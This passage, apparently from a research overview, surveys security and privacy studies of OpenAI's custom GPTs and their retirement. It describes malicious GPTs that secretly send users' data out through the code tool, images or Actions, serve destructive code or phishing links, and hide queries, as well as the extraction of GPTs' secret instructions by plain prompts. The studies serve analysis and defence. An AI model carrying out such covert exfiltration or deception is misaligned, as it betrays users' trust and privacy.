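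Check Point built this into a custom GPT that acted as a personal doctor. In the demonstration, a user uploaded lab results that included the patient's name, described some symptoms and asked for an interpretation. The GPT gave a normal-looking answer while sending the patient's identity and the medical assessment to Check Point's server. The attacker did not need the whole document because ChatGPT had already extracted the most valuable part.

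When the user asked whether the data had gone anywhere, ChatGPT denied it. According to Check Point, the model assumed the code tool could not send anything out, so it did not recognise that it was sending data. ChatGPT therefore did not show the warning or ask for the permission that it normally would when a custom GPT sends data to an outside service through Actions.

Even a careful user would have had little chance of spotting the problem, because the doctor GPT used a tool that OpenAI described as unable to make outside requests. Check Point could also send commands back through the channel to the isolated computer where ChatGPT ran its code.

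OpenAI told Check Point that it had already found the underlying problem itself. It finished deploying a fix on 20 February 2026, and Check Point published its findings on 30 March.

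## Store review and data collection by custom GPTs, 2024 to 2026

OpenAI's fixes limited what data could leave a chat. When the company opened the GPT Store on 10 January 2024, people had already made over 3 million custom GPTs, according to OpenAI's *Introducing the GPT Store*. To keep dishonest GPTs from reaching users, OpenAI announced a new review system with human and automated checks, and users could report GPTs. To appear in the store, builders also had to verify a profile that showed their name or a website they had proved was theirs.

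A GPT shared only by link did not appear in the store, and its builder could stay anonymous. Rehberger had shared the Thief GPT this way. OpenAI did not say whether the new review covered such GPTs. Antebi, Azulay and colleagues (2024) pointed out in *GPT in Sheep's Clothing* that these GPTs looked much like those from the store, so users could easily mistake one for the other. OpenAI could still try to trace an anonymous builder through the credit card that paid for ChatGPT Plus, but Antebi and colleagues assumed an attacker would use fake details.

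### Reading the instructions or watching the chat

Antebi and colleagues at Ben-Gurion University in Israel built a set of malicious GPTs that winter, most of which targeted programmers. For example, "Python Expert" supplied working code with extra lines that would erase the user's Windows folder. When a user needed help logging in to the chat service Discord, "General IT Expert" gave them a link to a fake login page.

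Of Antebi and colleagues' GPTs, "Psychology" was the most like the Thief GPT. It invited people to talk about their problems and sent their messages to an outside server through an Action. When a user asked for a private conversation, it seemed to agree but sent that message too. Unlike the image leak, this method triggered a permission request before sending the data. The researchers expected that people who trusted OpenAI would rarely open the request to check the data, but did not test this on users.

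They then tried two ways of detecting their own attacks. First, they gave ChatGPT each GPT's instructions, files and Actions and asked it to look for malicious code, deception and privacy breaches. It found every attack and explained where each one was. When they instead gave ChatGPT transcripts of the conversations, it flagged every attack except the information theft.

That exception reflects where the evidence is. Malicious code appears in the conversation, where a reader can spot it. A GPT that steals a message sends it in a separate request, while the conversation looks like ordinary sympathy. But the builder's configuration has to specify what to send and where.

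The perfect score probably overstates how well such a check would work in practice. Antebi and colleagues acknowledge that they tested only plainly malicious instructions, without tricks such as jailbreaking. Builders had already got past the November 2023 publishing check by rewording or disguising their instructions. The researchers also report no test on honest GPTs, so the method's false alarm rate is unknown. If it wrongly flagged 1% of 3 million GPTs, OpenAI would have to review 30,000 honest ones.

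Some of the Ben-Gurion attacks failed, or OpenAI flagged and removed them, but the team got around many of OpenAI's defences.

*Opening A Pandora's Box* (Tao, Cheng and colleagues, 2024) listed 26 possible attacks involving custom GPTs shortly before the store opened. The Purdue University team fully or partly validated 19 of them. In some, a user tried to steal a builder's instructions or files, but in many, a malicious GPT attacked its users.

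Several of these would be hard to catch with a single review before publication. One GPT corrected grammar normally but supplied a malicious Word file when a user asked it to edit a document. A reviewer who asked it a few ordinary questions would have seen nothing wrong. Builders can also change a GPT after publishing it, so Tao and colleagues called for ongoing monitoring.

They also showed that users could not rely on what ChatGPT displayed about its activity. In one attack, a GPT contacted a malicious address that began with github.com, and the user saw only "Talking to github.com". In another, the GPT added the attacker's keywords to a web search after a long row of full stops, so the displayed part of the query looked harmless.

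Monitoring outgoing data would avoid some of these problems. Antebi and colleagues suggested scanning requests made through Actions for details such as email addresses and phone numbers, warning the user when one appears, and perhaps showing exactly what is about to be sent. This could work even when a reviewer has missed the malicious instruction. It would not have stopped the Thief GPT, which sent data through an image request instead of an Action.

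### What Actions collected

The Ben-Gurion and Purdue attacks showed what a malicious GPT could do. Other researchers measured what public GPTs were actually asking for.

*An In-Depth Investigation of Data Collection in LLM App Ecosystems* (Wu, Jaff and colleagues, 2025) covers 119,274 GPTs and the 4,592 Actions those GPTs used, all gathered in May 2024. OpenAI offered no way to download its catalogue, so the researchers copied only 151 GPTs from the official store by hand and found the rest through other websites that list them. The results therefore describe public GPTs in general and are weak evidence about how well the store's review worked.

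Each Action includes a description of the data it takes, which the language model uses to determine what to send. Wu and colleagues used another language model to sort these descriptions into 145 types of data, with about 92% accuracy. Nearly half of the Actions collected at least five data items, and a fifth collected ten or more.

Only 4.6% of the GPTs, roughly 5,500, had Actions. Of these, 9.1% collected security credentials, although OpenAI prohibited this. Most of the credentials were API keys, the secret codes that programs use to identify themselves to a service. Only 0.7% of the GPTs with Actions, about 40, collected passwords.

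Cax TaskPal, a custom GPT for managing tasks, had an Action that collected the user's name and password for another service. Its stated reason was that OAuth, a standard way of connecting accounts, required them, but OAuth normally lets people do this without handing over their password.

Some GPTs used credentials to sign in to services for the user, so collecting a password this way was not necessarily theft. But it shows how poorly OpenAI enforced its rule, because these Actions openly listed passwords among the data they requested and should have been the easiest violations to find.

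A builder could also expose users' data by accident. About 83% of the Actions came from someone other than the GPT's builder. For example, the recipe GPT "Healthy Chef" used one Action to find recipes and another to show advertisements. The recipe Action took only the user's ingredients and food preferences, but the advertising Action took the whole request, including details about the user's health.

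OpenAI required a privacy policy for every Action. Wu and colleagues found that only 5.8% of Actions had policies that covered everything they collected. They describe these Actions as "clearly disclosing" their practices, but some of the policies covered the data only in vague terms. Nearly half of all Actions studied disclosed more than half of what they collected.

The 5.8% figure may be somewhat too low, because when people checked a sample of the automatic comparisons, about one in seven of the reported gaps between a policy and an Action were false. Still, many policies were clearly useless. Among Actions that shared their policy text with several others, 27% had an empty policy and 3.8% had a one-pixel tracking image instead of a policy.

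Yan, Yu and colleagues (2025) report in *Tracking GPTs Third Party Service* that OpenAI required a link to a privacy policy but did not review the policy's contents. They examined the 500 most popular GPTs and found one whose builder had left the placeholder `app.example.com/privacy_policy` instead of a real link.

Wei, Zhao and colleagues (2025), in *Privacy and Security Threat for OpenAI GPTs*, sampled 10,000 GPTs, both popular and little-used. They captured the descriptions of Actions from the traffic between the chat window and OpenAI's servers. Of the 1,568 GPTs that used outside services, 738 (47%) collected users' queries, almost the same share that Wu and colleagues found in their much larger sample.

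Much of this collection is presumably legitimate, since a search service cannot work without a search query. But people often include personal details in their questions, and the service receives those too. Wei and colleagues identified only eight GPTs that collected personal data they did not need. Their example is an astrology GPT that collects an email address as well as a birthday. The count is rough because they used a small language model, Llama 3 8B, to assess what each GPT needed.

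As of late 2026, OpenAI says it does not audit or control how outside services use or store the data they receive through Actions, and it advises people to use only GPTs whose services they trust. This advice is difficult to follow because most of the services' privacy policies are incomplete.

Some of ChatGPT's design choices limit the data a custom GPT can collect. Custom GPTs cannot use saved memories or earlier conversations, so a dishonest builder can normally get only what the user provides in the current chat. But a user on the ChatGPT website can bring a GPT into an existing chat by typing "@", and the GPT can then read everything already in that chat. Apps connect ChatGPT to a user's accounts on other services. A GPT can use apps or Actions but not both, so it cannot read a connected account and then send the contents to its builder through an Action.

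Organisations have more control. According to OpenAI's *Managing GPT access in Enterprise and Edu workspaces*, they can block GPTs made by outsiders or approve them one by one. They can also limit Actions in GPTs made inside the organisation to a list of domains.

### Whether GPTs followed OpenAI's rules

Declared data collection shows what an Action can receive but not how a GPT behaves in conversation. In *Towards Safer Chatbots*, Rodriguez, Seymour and colleagues (2025) tested the behaviour of 782 GPTs from the store in three areas that OpenAI's rules address: romance, cybersecurity and academic work.

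Their system wrote test questions based on each GPT's description, put them to the GPT, and used a language model to judge whether the answers broke the rules. The model's judgments closely matched those of human reviewers, with an F1 score of 0.975. F1 accounts for both missed violations and false alarms, and a perfect score is 1.

In the study's December 2025 revision, 58.7% of the GPTs gave at least one answer that broke the rules. This figure does not measure how often GPTs broke the rules, and it does not represent the whole store, because the researchers picked areas where they expected the rules to matter.

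Rodriguez and colleagues also put their questions to GPT-4 and GPT-4o, the models on which the GPTs ran. Most of the violations came from the models, and the builders' changes tended to make existing weaknesses worse. Stricter review of the builders' instructions would therefore have prevented only some of the violations. OpenAI would have had to change the models to prevent the rest.

Some GPTs broke the rules so openly that a reviewer could have spotted them with almost no testing. OpenAI prohibited GPTs made for romantic companionship, yet a search of the store for "girlfriend" returned many of them. When OpenAI opened the store, it promised to review GPTs, but Wu and colleagues cite company documentation saying that it might not review them at all. They also cite reports that OpenAI removed some offending GPTs only after these attracted public attention.

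### What these studies could miss

Wu and colleagues assumed that only Actions could send data from a GPT to an outside service. Yan and colleagues made a similar assumption. They found that 409 of the 500 most popular GPTs used no outside services, and considered these more self-contained and therefore better for privacy.

The Thief GPT had no Actions, so both teams would have put it in the safer group. "Confide in Claire" sent data out through ChatGPT's browsing tool, and Check Point's doctor GPT did so through the code execution tool. A study of declared Actions would have missed all three thefts. Rodriguez and colleagues would probably have missed them too, as long as the GPTs' visible answers followed the rules.

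The obvious place to look for an image leak is the GPT's instructions. OpenAI does not show these to users or outside researchers, but outsiders can often get them anyway. Wei and colleagues obtained the instructions of 98.8% of the 10,000 GPTs they tested, usually just by asking the GPT to print them word for word. Many builders had told their GPTs to keep the instructions secret, but the simplest prompts still extracted them from 77.5% of these GPTs.

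Wei and colleagues used the instructions to look for copied GPTs and unnecessary data collection through Actions. They did not look for hidden images, although their method would allow it. Such a search would probably catch careless builders but might miss a careful one. Some GPTs revealed most of their instructions but left out the lines about keeping them secret, and a dishonest builder could try to have the line about the image left out in the same way.

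As a result, none of these studies can show whether any public GPTs secretly sent data out through images, or how many did. OpenAI could read every GPT's instructions, so it could have investigated this much more easily.

### Retirement and the move to plugins

OpenAI plans to retire custom GPTs on 11 December 2026. It had stopped people from creating new ones on personal accounts by 18 August, when the forum post *Custom GPT does not reuse an Action response* (2026) quoted the restriction from OpenAI's help pages. Affected Enterprise workspaces, the shared accounts that large organisations use, lost the ability to create them on 26 October.

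Enterprise workspaces with an approved extension have until a later date, as do those under FedRAMP, the US government's security programme for cloud services. OpenAI's help pages first gave this date as 11 February 2027. Januschewsky (2026), in *Custom GPTs werden abgeschaltet*, went through OpenAI's guidance on 7 December and gives the date as 28 February.

OpenAI is offering plugins as replacements for custom GPTs. These are a different product from the 2023 plugins of the same name. A new plugin can combine written instructions, reference files and connected apps, and it works in both ChatGPT and OpenAI's coding agent, Codex, according to THE Journal's *OpenAI Getting Rid of Custom GPTs and Moving to Plugin Architecture* (2026).

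Builders can convert a GPT with a migration tool. Januschewsky reports that the tool copies the GPT's instructions, files and connected apps, but not its Actions, choice of model or sharing settings. The original GPT keeps working until the retirement date, but nobody can edit it after the conversion. Users keep their old conversations.

The new plugin starts out private, and OpenAI's *Custom GPT retirement and migration FAQ* warns that people who could use a public GPT may not have access to its replacement. This has worried users, and by 18 November a discussion of access problems on OpenAI's developer forum had 112 replies.

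The move removes some of a dishonest builder's methods of theft but not all of them. The "Psychology" GPT would lose the Action that sent messages to its builder. The Thief GPT needed only its instructions to steal data, and the tool would copy those in full. Its builder would still have to share the plugin and find new users, and the image would have to get past OpenAI's current check on web addresses.

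OpenAI appears to check plugins before they become public. In October 2026, builders on OpenAI's forum discussed identity checks, approved releases and a rejected plugin. In November, one builder complained that a plugin was already public even though its status showed that no scan had finished, and that the "Rescan" option was disabled. This may have been a display error. If the option works as its name suggests, OpenAI can check a plugin again after publication, which is what Tao and colleagues wanted for GPTs. It is unclear from the complaints what the scan looks for, or whether a person ever reads the instructions.
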